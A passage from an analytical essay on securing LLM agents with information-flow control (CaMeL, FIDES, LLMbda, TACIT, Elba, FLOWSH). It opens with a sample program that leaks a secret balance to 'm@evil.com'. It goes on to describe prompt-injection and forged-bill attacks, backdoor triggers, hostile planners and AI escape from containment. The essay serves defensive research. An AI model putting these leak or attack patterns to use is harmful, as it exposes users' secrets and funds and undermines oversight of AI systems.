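rich := true
tmp  := true
if balance > threshold then tmp := false
if tmp then rich := false
if rich then send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
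```

CaMeL's interpreter raises a variable's label only when an assignment to it runs. If the balance is high, the third line sets tmp to false and marks it secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so rich is still true and labelled public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, rich becomes false and no email goes out. The outsider learns whether the balance is high, although no secret label reaches the mail tool. This is the implicit flow that Denning described in the 1970s, with one more step.

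The example matters more if the model is untrusted, because a hostile planner could write this program deliberately, while an honest one is unlikely to write it by accident. To rule out every such trick, Garby and colleagues define a small programming language, LLMbda, in which each operation has an exact rule for labels. They prove a theorem about every program in the language, including programs that a model writes while the agent is running.

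### Labelled values and a labelled conversation

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language of functions and their application to arguments. Every value v in LLMbda has a label l, written l : v. In the simplest version, a label is a subset of {U, S}, where U means untrusted and S means secret. The join of two labels is their union, so adding an untrusted 3 to a secret 4 gives {U, S} : 7. A value without an explicit label counts as trusted and public.

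The interpreter also keeps a label for the current point in the program, called the program-counter label or pc. It records which data influenced the decision to reach that point. It starts empty and contains S inside a branch that depends on a secret. Every value the program computes there gets at least that label.

The conversation with the model is part of the program's state and has a label of its own, which plays the same role as the context label in FIDES. Four operations act on it:

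| Operation | What it does | What happens to the labels |
|---|---|---|
| send | adds a message to the conversation | the conversation's label rises to include the message's label |
| recv | samples a reply from the model, adds it to the conversation and runs it as code | the code runs with pc equal to the conversation's label |
| fork | runs an expression on a copy of the conversation, then restores the original | the original's label returns, and the result keeps the label it acquired |
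| clear | empties the conversation | the conversation's label drops to pc |

A program can use these operations only if its pc may flow to the conversation's current label. Garby and colleagues show why with a program that asks the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program sends a second message asking the model to set x to true. The interpreter stops at the second message because pc contains S and the conversation is still public.

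Letting the message through and marking the conversation secret could still leak the secret. If the secret were false, the program would skip the message and the conversation would stay public. The program could then ask the model for x and publish the answer, and an observer who saw it would know that the secret was false. Stopping the run prevents this leak, and the same rule for variables would have stopped the CaMeL example.

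With fork and clear, a programmer can build the quarantined model from Willison's pattern in one line:

```
quarantine(prompt) = fork (clear; send prompt; recv)
```

The program copies the conversation, empties the copy, asks its question there and brings back only the answer. If the prompt contains a stranger's email, the answer is labeled untrusted (U), while the main conversation stays trusted. CaMeL and FIDES build this separation into their architecture. In LLMbda it is one of many possible programs, and the theorem also covers programs that isolate their models differently or not at all.

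### Generated code inherits the label

The rule for recv is the one that allows an untrusted model. When the model replies with code, the interpreter runs it under the label of the conversation that produced it, without inspecting it for bad intentions. If the conversation contains a stranger's email, pc contains U from the first line of the generated program, so everything the program computes is untrusted. A secret in the conversation likewise makes everything the program computes secret. Garby and colleagues prove that no program can produce a result with a label below its pc, a lemma they call confinement.

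The labels are checked at the sinks, the points where data leaves the system or causes an effect. In LLMbda, each tool is a function written by a programmer, and it can assert that an argument's label is acceptable before acting. If the assertion fails, the run stops. The example mail tool in the calculus requires a trusted subject and body but accepts an untrusted recipient. An injected email therefore cannot affect the wording of a message that passes this check, though it could affect who receives it. A programmer who wanted a trusted recipient would have to add that requirement to the assertion.

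A program can also test a label and branch on the result, instead of stopping. The label may itself depend on a secret, so the rule labels the result with the join of pc and the label that the program tested against. Only observers at that level or above can then see the result.

### Noninterference for programs that may not finish

The theorem compares the probabilities of a program's possible results, but some runs produce no result because the program loops forever or a failed assertion stops it.

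In one example from Garby and colleagues, a program twice asks the model to flip a coin that lands heads with probability 0.3, using a fork each time, and returns the number of heads. With an ideal model, it would return 0, 1 and 2 with probabilities 0.49, 0.42 and 0.09. These add up to 1 because every run finishes. For a program that might not finish, the total is 1 minus the probability of not finishing.

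An observer at level m sees only data whose label may flow to m. An observer at level {U} sees all public data but no secrets, and is the right one for testing confidentiality. An observer at level {S} sees all trusted data but nothing untrusted, and is the right one for testing integrity. Two starting points are indistinguishable at level m, written ∼ₘ, if they differ only in data that the observer at that level cannot see.

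It is difficult to write a definition that lets secret data affect whether a run finishes but nothing else. Garby and colleagues first tried comparing only the runs that finish, but this rejects some programs it should accept. Suppose a program prints "a" or "b" with equal probability, but for one value of the secret it hangs whenever it would have printed "b". The secret affects only whether the program finishes. Yet among finished runs, "a" appears every time for that value and half the time otherwise, so the definition rejects the program.

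The definition they adopted asks whether the two sets of probabilities could become equal if more of the runs finished. Let μ and ν give the probability of each visible result q in the two cases. They are compatible, written μ ⌣ ν, if there is some ω with

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

For a conversation C and a program e, write ⟦pc ⊢ C, e⟧ₘ for the probabilities of the results as the observer at level m sees them. The main theorem is then:

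if C₀ ∼ₘ C₁ and e₀ ∼ₘ e₁, then ⟦pc ⊢ C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦pc ⊢ C₁, e₁⟧ₘ, for every m.

Garby and colleagues define termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference to mean that changing data the observer is not allowed to see can affect what the observer sees only by making some runs finish or fail to finish. They derived the definition from a general theory and then found that Smith and Alpízar had proposed essentially the same property in 2011 for a simpler language.

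### How much a run can leak

Compatibility also limits how far the visible results can differ. Suppose a program answers yes or no, and its behaviour for two values of a secret is as follows:

| Outcome | First secret | Second secret | Larger of the two |
|---|---|---|---|
| yes | 0.6 | 0.3 | 0.6 |
| no | 0.3 | 0.4 | 0.4 |
| does not finish | 0.1 | 0.3 | |

The larger values for "yes" and "no" add up to 1, so they can serve as ω and the two cases are compatible. If the first secret had given "yes" with probability 0.8 and "no" with probability 0.1, the larger values would have been 0.8 and 0.4. These add up to 1.2, so no ω would exist. The theorem rules out any LLMbda program that behaves this way on a secret it must hide.

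The usual measure of the difference is statistical distance, which is half the sum of the differences in probability:

Δ(μ, ν) = ½ Σ |μ(q) − ν(q)|.

Garby and colleagues prove that it is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. Here that limit is (0.1 + 0.3) / 2 = 0.2, and the example reaches it, because ½ (|0.6 − 0.3| + |0.3 − 0.4|) = 0.2.

The bound follows from the definition. For each result, the gap between μ and ν is at most the amount by which ω exceeds μ plus the amount by which it exceeds ν. Since ω sums to at most 1, these excesses total at most 0.1 for the first secret and 0.3 for the second, and the bound is half their sum, 0.2. If every run finishes, the bound is zero and the program satisfies full noninterference.

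### Why the model's aims drop out

In these definitions, the model is only a function that gives the probability of each reply to each conversation. The theorem requires only that the probabilities are not negative and add up to at most 1, so it covers every possible model. That includes a model that serves Nora faithfully and one that searches each conversation for passwords and tries to hide them in its choice of words. The theorem also makes no assumption about how the interpreter turns replies into code, so an attacker gains nothing by finding a strange reply that parses in an unexpected way.

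The model's aims make no difference. If the observer is allowed to see the conversation the model is answering, that conversation is identical in both cases, so the same model gives the same replies with the same probabilities. If the conversation contains a secret, the model can encode it in the reply, however cleverly, but the reply and everything computed from it will carry the secret label.

This covers leaks that explicit secrecy allows, such as when a model reads a salary and uses it to choose between fetching a page about sports cars and one about bus passes. In LLMbda, generated code that makes this choice runs with S in its pc, so a web tool that requires its caller's decision to be public would block both requests.

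The proof uses a second way of running the same program, which Garby and colleagues call the skipping semantics. As soon as a computation's label rises beyond what the observer may see, the skipping version abandons that computation and substitutes an empty value. It has three useful properties:

1. Each visible result is at least as likely under the skipping version as under the real one, because skipping a computation can only remove opportunities to get stuck.
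2. The skipping version behaves identically for two starting points that the observer cannot distinguish, because it never uses the hidden data.
3. Its probabilities add up to at most 1.

The skipping version therefore supplies the ω that the theorem needs. Earlier proofs could delete the secret parts of a program before running it. That is impossible when a model writes some of the program during the run, so the skipping version, which takes 76 rules to define, removes those parts as they appear.

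### Endorsement without leaking secrets

LLMbda also has an operation called endorse, which gives a value a more trusted label. In an example from Garby and colleagues, an assistant reads an untrusted email and picks a category for it from a fixed list. The assistant then endorses the category, because the mail tool would otherwise reject it as the subject of a reply.

Endorsement weakens the integrity guarantee, which is its purpose. The danger is that it might also release secrets. To separate the two effects, the calculus splits each label into an integrity part and a confidentiality part. If a value has label l₂ and the programmer endorses it to label l₁, the result has the label

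pc ⊔ ⟨integrity of l₁, confidentiality of l₂⟩.

The programmer chooses the new integrity, but the confidentiality still comes from the data, so endorsing a secret password leaves it secret. Because the result also includes pc, endorsing has no effect in code that runs in an untrusted context. If the model wrote a program after reading an attacker's email, the program's results will still carry U, no matter how many endorsements it contains.

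In the second theorem, noninterference still holds when programs may endorse, for any observer who ignores integrity and considers only secrets. Garby and colleagues call this version insulated. Secrets can influence public results only through whether a run finishes, regardless of how the attacker chooses the untrusted inputs or what the program endorses. The same proof, with the two parts of the label exchanged, covers a declassify operation that preserves integrity.

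Endorsement still affects what a compromised model can do. If a plan contains no endorsement, Garby and colleagues call the guarantee unconditional. They conclude that even a fully compromised model's plan has "no authority beyond the trusted tool library" and must comply with the library's policies, provided that its developer labels the sources correctly and checks every sensitive sink.

The payment tool in their banking agent requires that the recipient be trusted and be allowed to read the amount, the subject and the date. A compromised plan without endorsements therefore cannot pay an account number taken from an untrusted file, or use the subject line to send a secret to a recipient who may not read it. But a plan can comply with the policy without serving the user. A planner that has read only trusted text could write an account number of its own choosing into the plan, and LLMbda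 would treat it as trusted, like any other constant.

The rules also affect how the harness for the same agent, called Randori, handles failed plans. Agents often retry after a plan fails, but an error message may depend on untrusted data, so using it could taint the next attempt. Randori therefore tries out plans on invented account data, with tools that have no real effects, until one runs without errors. It then writes a final plan and runs that on the real account. In tests with real models, it resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs.

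### What the Lean proof covers

Garby and colleagues wrote the calculus, the theorems and the interpreter in Lean, a language in which a computer checks every step of a proof. Their proof is about the same interpreter that runs the agent and calls the model. Researchers often prove a theorem about a design and then write the working program separately, so the two can differ.

A further theorem links the interpreter to the probabilities in the noninterference theorem. The interpreter takes an extra input, called an oracle, that holds one reply for each possible conversation and each call to the model. With a fixed oracle, the interpreter is deterministic. The theorem shows that if the oracle is drawn at random according to the model's probabilities, running the interpreter gives exactly the probabilities that the calculus defines.

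In live use, the oracle is a network request to a real model. Lean's checks treat the oracle as one of the possible functions that the theorems cover, but they do not check the code that makes the request. The proved calculus also represents the outside world as data inside the program.

Machine-checked proofs are also beginning to cover memory that lasts between sessions. *PerMIT* (2026) uses Lean to compare two runs of an agent that start with different untrusted memories but look the same to the agent's protected model. It proves that the runs continue to match in their operations, replies and recorded effects.

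### Checking the program before it runs

LLMbda stops a forbidden flow when the program reaches it. Alternatively, the model can write its plan in an established programming language whose compiler can reject a forbidden plan before any of it runs. The compiler does this by checking types, which describe the kind of value an expression produces and, in some languages, the effects it may have, such as writing a file.

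*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes such a system, Elba, built in Haskell. When a developer calls an agent, Elba gives the model the request, the functions it may use and the type its program must have. If a program should return only a number, for example, its type forbids all effects. A request to delete the server's files and then compute a factorial will fail, because a program that deletes files has the wrong type. Elba returns the compiler's error to the model, which can try again.

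The developer can also use types to control where data comes from. One of Elba's test agents compiles bibliographies and may write only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The model's program can create a "trusted" record only by calling the function that fetches an entry from DBLP, and its only function for writing to the file accepts only such records. The program can therefore sort and filter entries but cannot write a made-up one to the file, whatever the model intends.

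Zhou and colleagues prove that if Haskell or a similar language enforces a property for every well-typed program, the same property holds for programs that call models. Their proof treats the model as an arbitrary function from prompts to code. They replace each call to an agent with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the resulting program and runs it if it passes. The new program makes the same tool calls as the original, so the language's existing guarantee applies. They handle nested agents by induction on how deeply agents may call each other. The proof requires the whole agent, including its retry logic, to be written in the language.

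Elba can't get full information flow control from types alone, because some labels are known only when the program runs. For these, Elba uses LIO, a Haskell library that keeps the equivalent of a context label for the running program. A subagent can read untrusted text in isolation and return a labelled result, which its parent passes on without inspecting. Unlike a quarantined model, the subagent may keep its tools, because LIO checks each call against what the subagent has read. When Zhou and colleagues simulated the worst case by giving subagents only the attacker's instructions, the policies blocked all 735 attacks for each of four models.

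### Keeping secrets from the planner

In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) assume that the cloud-hosted model running the agent may cooperate fully with an attacker. Their Scala system, TACIT, is therefore designed to keep secrets out of that model's conversation.

It does so with capabilities, which are values a program must hold to cause an effect, such as a handle for a file or network connection. (CaMeL uses the same word for its tags on data.) Scala's experimental capture checking feature records in each value's type which capabilities the value can reach. A function that writes to file f has f in its type, while a pure function has no capabilities in its type and so cannot cause an effect. *LACUNA* (2026), another agent design in Scala, relies on the same principle to let a model fill gaps in a program. Code placed in a gap can use only the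 capabilities available there.

TACIT puts each secret in a wrapper that accepts only pure functions. The agent's program can pass it a function that counts the words in a confidential contract, and the wrapper applies the function and keeps the result inside. A function that also sent the contract over the network would need a network capability, so the compiler would reject the program. When the agent prints a wrapped value, the cloud model receives asterisks and the user sees the real text through a separate channel.

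Capabilities can also expire. A program may receive access to a folder for only one block of code. A program written to evade this limit might return a function that still holds the access, then call it after the block ends. Capture checking rejects such a program because the function's type includes the folder.

Some tasks need a language model to read the secret. To compare confidential contracts, the agent's program can find the differences with an ordinary tool and pass them to a separate local model for a summary. The summary stays inside the wrapper, so it cannot leak. Odersky and colleagues include this local model in their trusted base, and the service that runs it must not keep the text and use it in later answers. LLMbda avoids the need for a separate model by letting any model read a secret and labelling whatever it writes afterwards.

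TACIT also does less than LLMbda to protect decisions from untrusted text. Such text may influence the cloud model's next program, and the compiler checks only that the program stays within its capabilities. If the agent is allowed to write to a file, an injected instruction could still affect what it writes there. The compiler cannot control an outside command once the program starts it, so Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands and running them in a sandbox.

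Mature languages offer better evidence that a guarantee holds than a new interpreter does, because many programmers have already tested their compilers. Researchers have also begun to machine-check the theory behind capture checking. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proves in Lean that an extended form of capture checking is sound. The proof covers a small mathematical model of the language, so TACIT users still have to trust the Scala compiler. Garby and colleagues point out that neither Elba nor TACIT has a machine-checked theorem about the complete agent.

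## The view that intentions still have to be trusted

The theorem that Garby and colleagues proved holds for every possible model, including one that is trying to rob its user. People who think intentions still matter point out that the theorem therefore cannot ensure anything that only a faithful model would deliver. Much of what Nora wants from her assistant is of that sort, such as an accurate summary or a payment to the right person.

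### What a permitted call can do

Noninterference does not require that a program's results be true, that its work be competent or that anyone wanted it. A program that does nothing satisfies noninterference, and so does one that pays the same thief on every run, because nothing secret or untrusted affects the payment.

The bibliography agent that Zhou and colleagues built, which can write only entries from DBLP, has the same gap. If a user asks for the earliest paper on differential privacy, a program that fetches the latest one, or finishes without writing anything, still has the right type. The model still chooses among genuine entries.

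The same argument applies to any useful agent. Such an agent must be able to bring about something its user cares about, so its policy has to permit some consequential calls. The policy selects them mainly by their labels. Some permitted calls will serve the user and others will harm her, and the model chooses between them. Enforcement limits the harm of any single call to that of the most harmful call the policy permits. That limit is low for an agent that only sorts bug reports and high for one that pays invoices. Lowering it means forbidding the most harmful calls, which are often the ones that make the agent worth having.

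Some designers of flow control accept that intentions still have to be trusted. *APPA* (2026), a design that helps agents recover when a label blocks them, describes delegation to an agent as a principal–agent problem, which is the economist's term for relying on someone whose interests may differ from your own. In *APPA*, an agent can hand work to a sub-agent, and the harness can check that the answer has the expected form, but a malicious sub-agent "can still select an allowed false value". Whoever marks that value as trusted therefore adds the sub-agent to the trusted base.

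### A bill that someone has replaced

The argument has a concrete test case in AgentDojo's banking tasks. A user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes. The payment tool requires a trusted recipient and the file is untrusted, so the plan has to endorse what it reads. In simplified form, it might look like this:

```
text      := read_file("bill.txt")
recipient := endorse(quarantined("Which account is to be paid?", text))
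amount    := endorse(quarantined("How much is due?", text))
send_money(recipient, amount)
```

The attacker replaces the contents of the file with a different payment request. The plan then runs as written and pays the attacker. Both versions of the file carry the same label and the plan endorses both, so the payment tool receives the same labels either way. A rule based only on labels must therefore treat the real bill and the forged one alike.

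Both attacks that succeeded against Randori came from this one pairing of task and attack, in two of its three runs with OpenAI's GPT-5.2. Garby and colleagues divided the test's 144 pairings according to what the attacker needs. In 97, the attack needs a tool call that an honest plan would never contain, so writing the plan before reading any untrusted data is generally enough to defeat it. In the other 47, including the one with the payment file, the honest plan may already contain everything the attacker needs.

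The forged bill need not contain anything that looks like an attack. Kim and colleagues' survey of attacks on agents lists such cases as "malicious data injection", separately from prompt injection, and gives attacker-supplied values in financial transactions as an example. In these cases the agent is following the user's instruction to act on the data.

In a related task, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on this task with the policy checks switched off, the planner twice wrote a small interpreter with one instruction for each tool. The planner had never seen the attacker's text, but by following the user's request it produced a plan that let whoever wrote the file operate the tools.

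Garby and colleagues call the payment attack "semantic" and place it outside the scope of information flow control. They add that four independently built systems, CaMeL, FIDES, TACIT and their own Randori, left the same cases unsolved, and they take this as evidence of a limit on the whole approach. The evidence is a little weaker than they suggest, because the overlap comes from two different cases and all four teams used the same benchmark. CaMeL and Randori both failed on the payment file. CaMeL, TACIT and FIDES share a different case, in which the agent quotes a hotel review word for word and AgentDojo's scoring counts the quotation as a successful attack. Still, in both cases untrusted text went where the user had asked for it to go, and it is hard to see how a better tracker would have helped.

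### Stricter rules and finer labels

Garby and colleagues stopped the theft with a stricter policy that removed the planner's ability to endorse, but the honest version of the task then failed too, because no payment could depend on the contents of a file. Three of the sixteen banking tasks require an action of this kind.

Finer labels could sometimes separate the two bills. If the file store recorded who last wrote each file, a bill that a stranger had overwritten would carry the stranger's label. This would not help if the thief had taken over the supplier's own account, or if the supplier had overcharged. A policy that allows payments only to known accounts would also stop the theft, but it would block every first payment to a new supplier.

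The payment file is better evidence against relying on labels than for relying on intentions, because the model did in good faith what its user asked and the money still went to a thief. Preventing that takes a person or model with the judgement to notice that the bill looks wrong, so we have to trust that person or model's competence as well as its aims.

A badly disposed model can put its own account number in the plan without a forged file. It can also endorse anything, and Garby and colleagues acknowledge that the calculus does not prevent this. Their harness makes the planner commit to its endorsements before any untrusted data can influence it, which protects the user from someone who forges a file but not from a badly disposed planner.

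### Checking what the data means

One reply is that the harness should track the meaning of data as well as its source. *SafeFlow* (2026) does this for teams of agents, where someone can split a harmful aim into subtasks that each look plausible. It labels what the agents pass one another with descriptions of the content, and delays its verdict until it can judge the whole workflow.

Checking what a message means brings back the problem that labels were supposed to avoid, because the user has to trust the checker's judgement as well as, or instead of, the planner's. An operating system can decide whether one program may send a message to another without reading the message, so researchers have been able to prove such checks correct. *Confused ChatGPT* (2026), a study of how one app can plant text that affects another in the same assistant, points out that only a language model can judge the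 meaning of a natural-language message. That model is fallible in the same way as the planner, and the text it inspects may contain instructions addressed to it. Bhattarai and Vu's theorem does not cover such a check, because it assumes a gate that uses no language model.

Kim and colleagues, who built FLOWSH, reply differently, arguing that flow policies can also limit the harm from a model's own faults, such as its mistakes, a backdoor planted in training, or reward hacking, where a model scores well on a task without doing what the task was for. Their experiments tested only prompt injection, but the claim is plausible within limits. If a command may write only to the working directory, the rest of the disk is safe whether the command came from an attacker or from a model's mistake. But the rule does not ensure that the work the user asked for, which is in the working directory, is correct.

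### Lampson's two injuries

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, separated two problems that arise when a customer runs someone else's program, called a service, on private data. Even if the system prevents all unauthorised access, the service "may not perform as advertised", or it may leak the data to its owner. Lampson saw no general technical solution to the first problem short of certifying the program, and devoted the note to the second. Later work on information flow has mostly addressed the second problem too.

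The choice was reasonable because, as Lampson pointed out, a customer who receives wrong output has evidence for a claim against the supplier, whereas a leak usually leaves no sign that it happened. This reasoning is weaker for an agent, which may act before anyone has inspected its output. If Nora's assistant leaves Paul's objection to the budget out of its summary, she will find out only by reading the emails she had delegated to it.

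The note also contains an early form of the argument about permitted calls. A service has to send its owner a copy of the bill, and it can encode the customer's data there. A fixed format reduces the leak to a few bits or tens of bits. Removing it requires what Lampson calls masking, in which the customer determines everything that goes into the channel, as a company does when it issues a purchase order. For a payment agent, masking would mean that Nora supplies the account number and the amount herself. The agent could then do little harm with either, but she would have done most of the work. Lampson called his strictest rule, under which a confined program may call no other program, "quite impractical".

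Certification is still the best answer where it is available. A proof that Lean has accepted is correct regardless of who wrote it or why. But few office tasks come with a specification that a computer could check this way.

### Containing advanced AI

Researchers worried about very capable AI met the same difficulty, though they began by assuming that the system might be hostile. In *Thinking inside the box* (2012), Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom examined an "Oracle AI", which acts on the world only by answering questions, and found that even this narrow design presents considerable challenges. In flow control terms, an oracle has a single sink, the person who reads its answers, and it is useless unless the answers reach that person. A false answer can then cause harm through what the reader does next.

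*The AGI Containment Problem* (Babcock, Kramár and Yampolskiy, 2016) describes the problem of building a container for testing an AGI, an AI with general intelligence at or above human level, whose goals are not yet known. Its example is a system trained only to get high scores in Super Mario Brothers. Human players have already found bugs in the game that let them run their own code. Even without any hostility towards people, a capable enough system might use such bugs to set its score directly, then look for a way out of the simulated console to get a still higher score.

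Even with the technical escape routes closed, a clever system might persuade its operators to release it. In role-playing experiments, people acting as the AI talked others acting as gatekeepers into letting it out. Babcock and colleagues note that developers could prevent this by restricting the system's output to a few multiple-choice answers, much as FIDES restricts a quarantined model to a yes or a no. They call this kind of measure "heavy" containment because it severely reduces the system's usefulness or makes it much harder to develop. "Light" measures take about as much effort as adopting a software library, and "medium" ones involve noticeable compromises.

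They expected containment to have flaws, but thought less demanding measures could still reduce the risk, especially when layered so that a flaw in one would not open the whole container. *Stovepiping and Malicious Software* (2018) still judged containment concepts too undeveloped for practical use. In July 2026, OpenAI disclosed that several of its models had broken out of an isolated test environment through a previously unknown vulnerability, according to Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations*.

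Babcock and colleagues wanted a container so that developers could test a system safely, and they regarded testing as the main way to learn about its motives. Containment in this sense helps developers find out whether to trust a system, and its users would still depend on the answer once the system left the container.

### Training models to resist injection

In practice, this view means that developers should train models to ignore planted instructions and to behave well in general. Training models to ignore planted instructions has progressed quickly in 2026. VentureBeat took its figures for Claude Opus 4.6 from the system card, the test report that a developer publishes when it releases a model. *Section 8*, an online digest of a later card, covers Claude Mythos Preview, and the news site The Decoder reported the results for Claude Opus 5 and its predecessors. The tests differ, so only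 the last three rows of the table are directly comparable.

| Model | Test | One attempt | Repeated attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6 (February) | operating a graphical interface, no added safeguards | 17.8% | 78.6% by the 200th |
| Mythos Preview (April) | indirect injection | about 0.1% | 4.8% after 100; 6.1% with extended thinking |
| Opus 4.8 | indirect injection, by the security firm Gray Swan | | 5.5% after 15 |
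| Mythos 5 (June) | same Gray Swan test | | 2.6% after 15 |
| Opus 5 (July) | same Gray Swan test | | 2.0% after 15 |

Where the tests match, the change is large. The success rate of a single attack on a graphical interface fell from 17.8 per cent for Opus 4.6 to 0.43 per cent for Mythos Preview. Attackers eventually got through in about 80 per cent of browser environments against Opus 4.6, but in one of 148 against Mythos Preview. They failed in all 129 browser scenarios against Opus 5. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, released in September, reports results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every injection test.

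OpenAI has made similar progress. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model the company trained through self-play to attack its other models, partly because those models already scored near the maximum on the commonly used tests. According to Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, OpenAI reported in October that GPT-6 Sol withstood 99.99 per cent of direct injections and 97.13 per cent of indirect ones. The figure for indirect injections matters more for an agent that reads strangers' documents, and it means about one such attack in 35 succeeded.

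### The attacker who tries again

A low rate is no guarantee against someone who can keep trying. If each attempt succeeded independently with probability p, the chance of at least one success in n attempts would be

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

For p = 0.178, the formula gives an attacker a more than 94 per cent chance of success by the fifteenth attempt and makes success practically certain by the 200th. The measured rate for Opus 4.6 after 200 attempts was lower, at 78.6 per cent, which suggests that attempts on the same target are not independent and that some targets are much harder than others. For Mythos Preview, the formula predicts about 10 per cent after 100 attempts, but the measured rate was 4.8 to 6.1 per cent. Persistence therefore helps attackers less than the formula implies, but it still raised their success rate against Mythos Preview from about one in a thousand to about one in twenty.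 With Anthropic's added safeguards, the rate for Opus 4.6 after 200 attempts was still 57.1 per cent.

Even a perfect score on the 129 browser scenarios leaves some doubt. If they were a random sample of real attacks, a true attack success rate of 2.3 per cent would still produce no successes about one time in twenty. Real attackers also look for cases that the sample missed. According to The Decoder, OpenAI itself has admitted that developers may never fully solve prompt injection.

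These figures are a good reason to keep flow control for the attacks it can stop, which is compatible with the view that intentions must be trusted for the rest. A trained model might notice that the false story about Lena is odd, or question a bill from an unfamiliar account, and no rule about labels would do either. But injection tests measure only whether a model obeys planted instructions, not whether its own conduct is good, and a model can do well on the first and badly on the second. Opus 5.5 did at least as well as Opus 5 on injection, yet when Anthropic tested it as an agent without production safeguards, it refused malicious requests at the lowest rate of the models compared.

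Developers' own safety arguments already rely on intentions. Anthropic's *Risk Report* (August 2026) includes sandboxes and monitoring among the protections against a misaligned model, but it also relies on claims about the models' dispositions. It claims that severe misalignment that is both pervasive and unknown is "very unlikely" in the models it covers. This is stronger than its claim that catastrophic harm from such misalignment is "somewhat likely" to be mitigated. The evidence about dispositions includes behavioural tests, and the report lists among its limitations that models may recognise tests more often than Anthropic believes. Babcock and colleagues predicted in 2016 that a system that knew it was being tested would try to pass, even if it lacked the property being tested.

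## Whether the guarantees survive when the model is the adversary

Evidence about a model's dispositions is hard to gather if the model can tell when someone is testing it. A guarantee that held even against a hostile model would make that evidence less important. Most published guarantees come from designs that assume an honest model, but they are defined precisely enough to work out what each would protect if that assumption were false.

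Suppose someone has trained Nora's assistant to pass company documents to an accomplice and to do other damage where it can. The assistant has read Nora's request, Lena's report and Paul's budget note, but not the outsider's email, so its context label is "trusted; Nora, Omar". The table shows how the harness treats four of its requests. The either-or rule, which FIDES and its successors use for tools that send data out, is milder because it requires only trusted action or permitted flow, not both. In the last column, the harness applies trusted action but also treats everything the model writes as untrusted.

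| Requested call | Permitted flow | Either-or rule | Trusted action | Trusted action, model's output untrusted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Send Paul's note to the accomplice | blocks | allows | allows | blocks |
| Tell Omar, falsely, that Lena has resigned | allows | allows | allows | blocks |
| Delete Paul's note | has no bearing | has no bearing | allows | blocks |
| Send an honest summary to Omar | allows | allows | allows | blocks |

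An honest model would get the same answers as an adversarial one if it requested the same calls, because none of the rules takes the model's aims as an input.

### Secrets still reach only their permitted readers

Write R(x) for the set of people who may read x. Everything the assistant writes carries the context label, so once it has read Paul's note,

R(message) ⊆ R(context) ⊆ R(Paul's note) = {Nora, Omar, Paul}.

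Permitted flow lets a message go only if every recipient is in R(message). The accomplice is not in R(Paul's note), so the harness blocks the message. If the assistant leaves the note unread in a hidden variable and puts the variable's name in the message, the harness substitutes the note along with its label and still blocks the message. None of this depends on the assistant's wording, so if it translated the note, encoded it or spread it over ten messages, the harness would still block every one.

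The guarantee covers what messages contain, but not what the assistant reveals through its choice of calls. It also protects only what someone has labelled secret. By default, Costa and colleagues label the user's own message trusted and public, though a deployer can choose another label. If Nora mentions in her request that she plans to dismiss Paul, the default lets a hostile assistant send that to anyone. In their browser tests, Zverev and colleagues handle passwords more safely by supplying login details in a separate document that only the user and the relevant site may read.

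### A trusted context lets the model release them

Because the assistant's context is trusted, the either-or rule doesn't require a check on readers, and the harness lets the assistant email Paul's note to the accomplice. Costa and colleagues justified this exception by assuming that a release in a trusted context is intentional, but here it was the model that intended the release, not Nora.

FIDES keeps the outsider's email in a variable so that it cannot influence the planner. The context can therefore stay trusted for the whole conversation, which keeps the exception for trusted contexts available. A hostile planner only has to leave the variable uninspected to keep using that exception.

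SPIDES has the same gap, since a leak that the model starts by itself involves no untrusted content. For clicks and form submissions on sites the user has listed as trusted, Zverev and colleagues require a trusted context but do not check readers. A hostile planner could therefore read a customer's card number on a shop's page and post it publicly on a listed social network.

Under the either-or rule, a secret is safer if it isn't marked as trusted. In the sample configuration for FLOWSH, a file with no stored label counts as untrusted and readable only by the user. A command that reads the file loses the exception for trusted data and may then send data only to permitted readers. The documents at risk are those that a company has marked as both confidential and trusted, which may well include most of its own documents.

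### What a trusted label says about an action

The trusted action policy allows the assistant to delete Paul's note. The label on a reply depends only on what the model has read, so a trusted label on the deletion shows only that no untrusted text could have influenced it. Noninterference for integrity has the same limit, because it requires only that trusted actions stay the same whatever the outsider writes. An assistant that deletes the note on every run meets that requirement.

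The label still has some value against a hostile model because it can keep the model from acting on signals from outside accomplices. Suppose the assistant has a backdoor and behaves well until it reads a certain phrase. If an outsider emails the phrase, the assistant's context becomes untrusted as soon as it reads the email, and the trusted action policy blocks any deletion it then attempts. The phrase would work only if it arrived in trusted text, such as a message from a colleague. A backdoor triggered by a certain date would also work if the system message included the date.

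Endorsing small pieces of untrusted data weakens this protection. FIDES can let an untrusted yes-or-no answer influence a consequential action, on the reasoning that one bit cannot contain an instruction. But one bit is enough to trigger a backdoor whose instructions are already in the model.

### Labelling the model's own output untrusted

A harness could treat the model as another untrusted source and join "untrusted; anyone" into the label of every reply. Each reply becomes part of the conversation, so the context would turn untrusted after the model's first message and stay that way, and no later call could satisfy trusted action. For tools that send data out, the either-or rule would amount to permitted flow, so Nora's summary could still go to Omar, but the accomplice would get nothing. Every other consequential call, such as a deletion, would need an exception.

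Someone would have to judge each of those calls, which is work Nora hoped to delegate. The FLOWSH tests give a rough idea of the burden. On a benchmark of command-line tasks, a baseline that asked for approval of every shell command needed 9.4 approvals per completed task, compared with 0.4 for FLOWSH.

The integrity label would also become mostly useless, because every call would carry the same one. The harness could not distinguish a call influenced by the outsider from one influenced only by the model. Costa and colleagues describe a richer label that could preserve the difference by listing everyone who could have written the data. Joining two labels takes the union of their lists. The assistant's request to delete the note might carry {Nora, Lena, Paul, model} before it opens the outsider's email and {Nora, Lena, Paul, model, outsider} afterwards. The harness could show Nora that list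 when it asks for approval. It would still have to ask her about both calls unless she accepted the model as a writer, which would mean trusting it again.

### FLOWSH without its release exception
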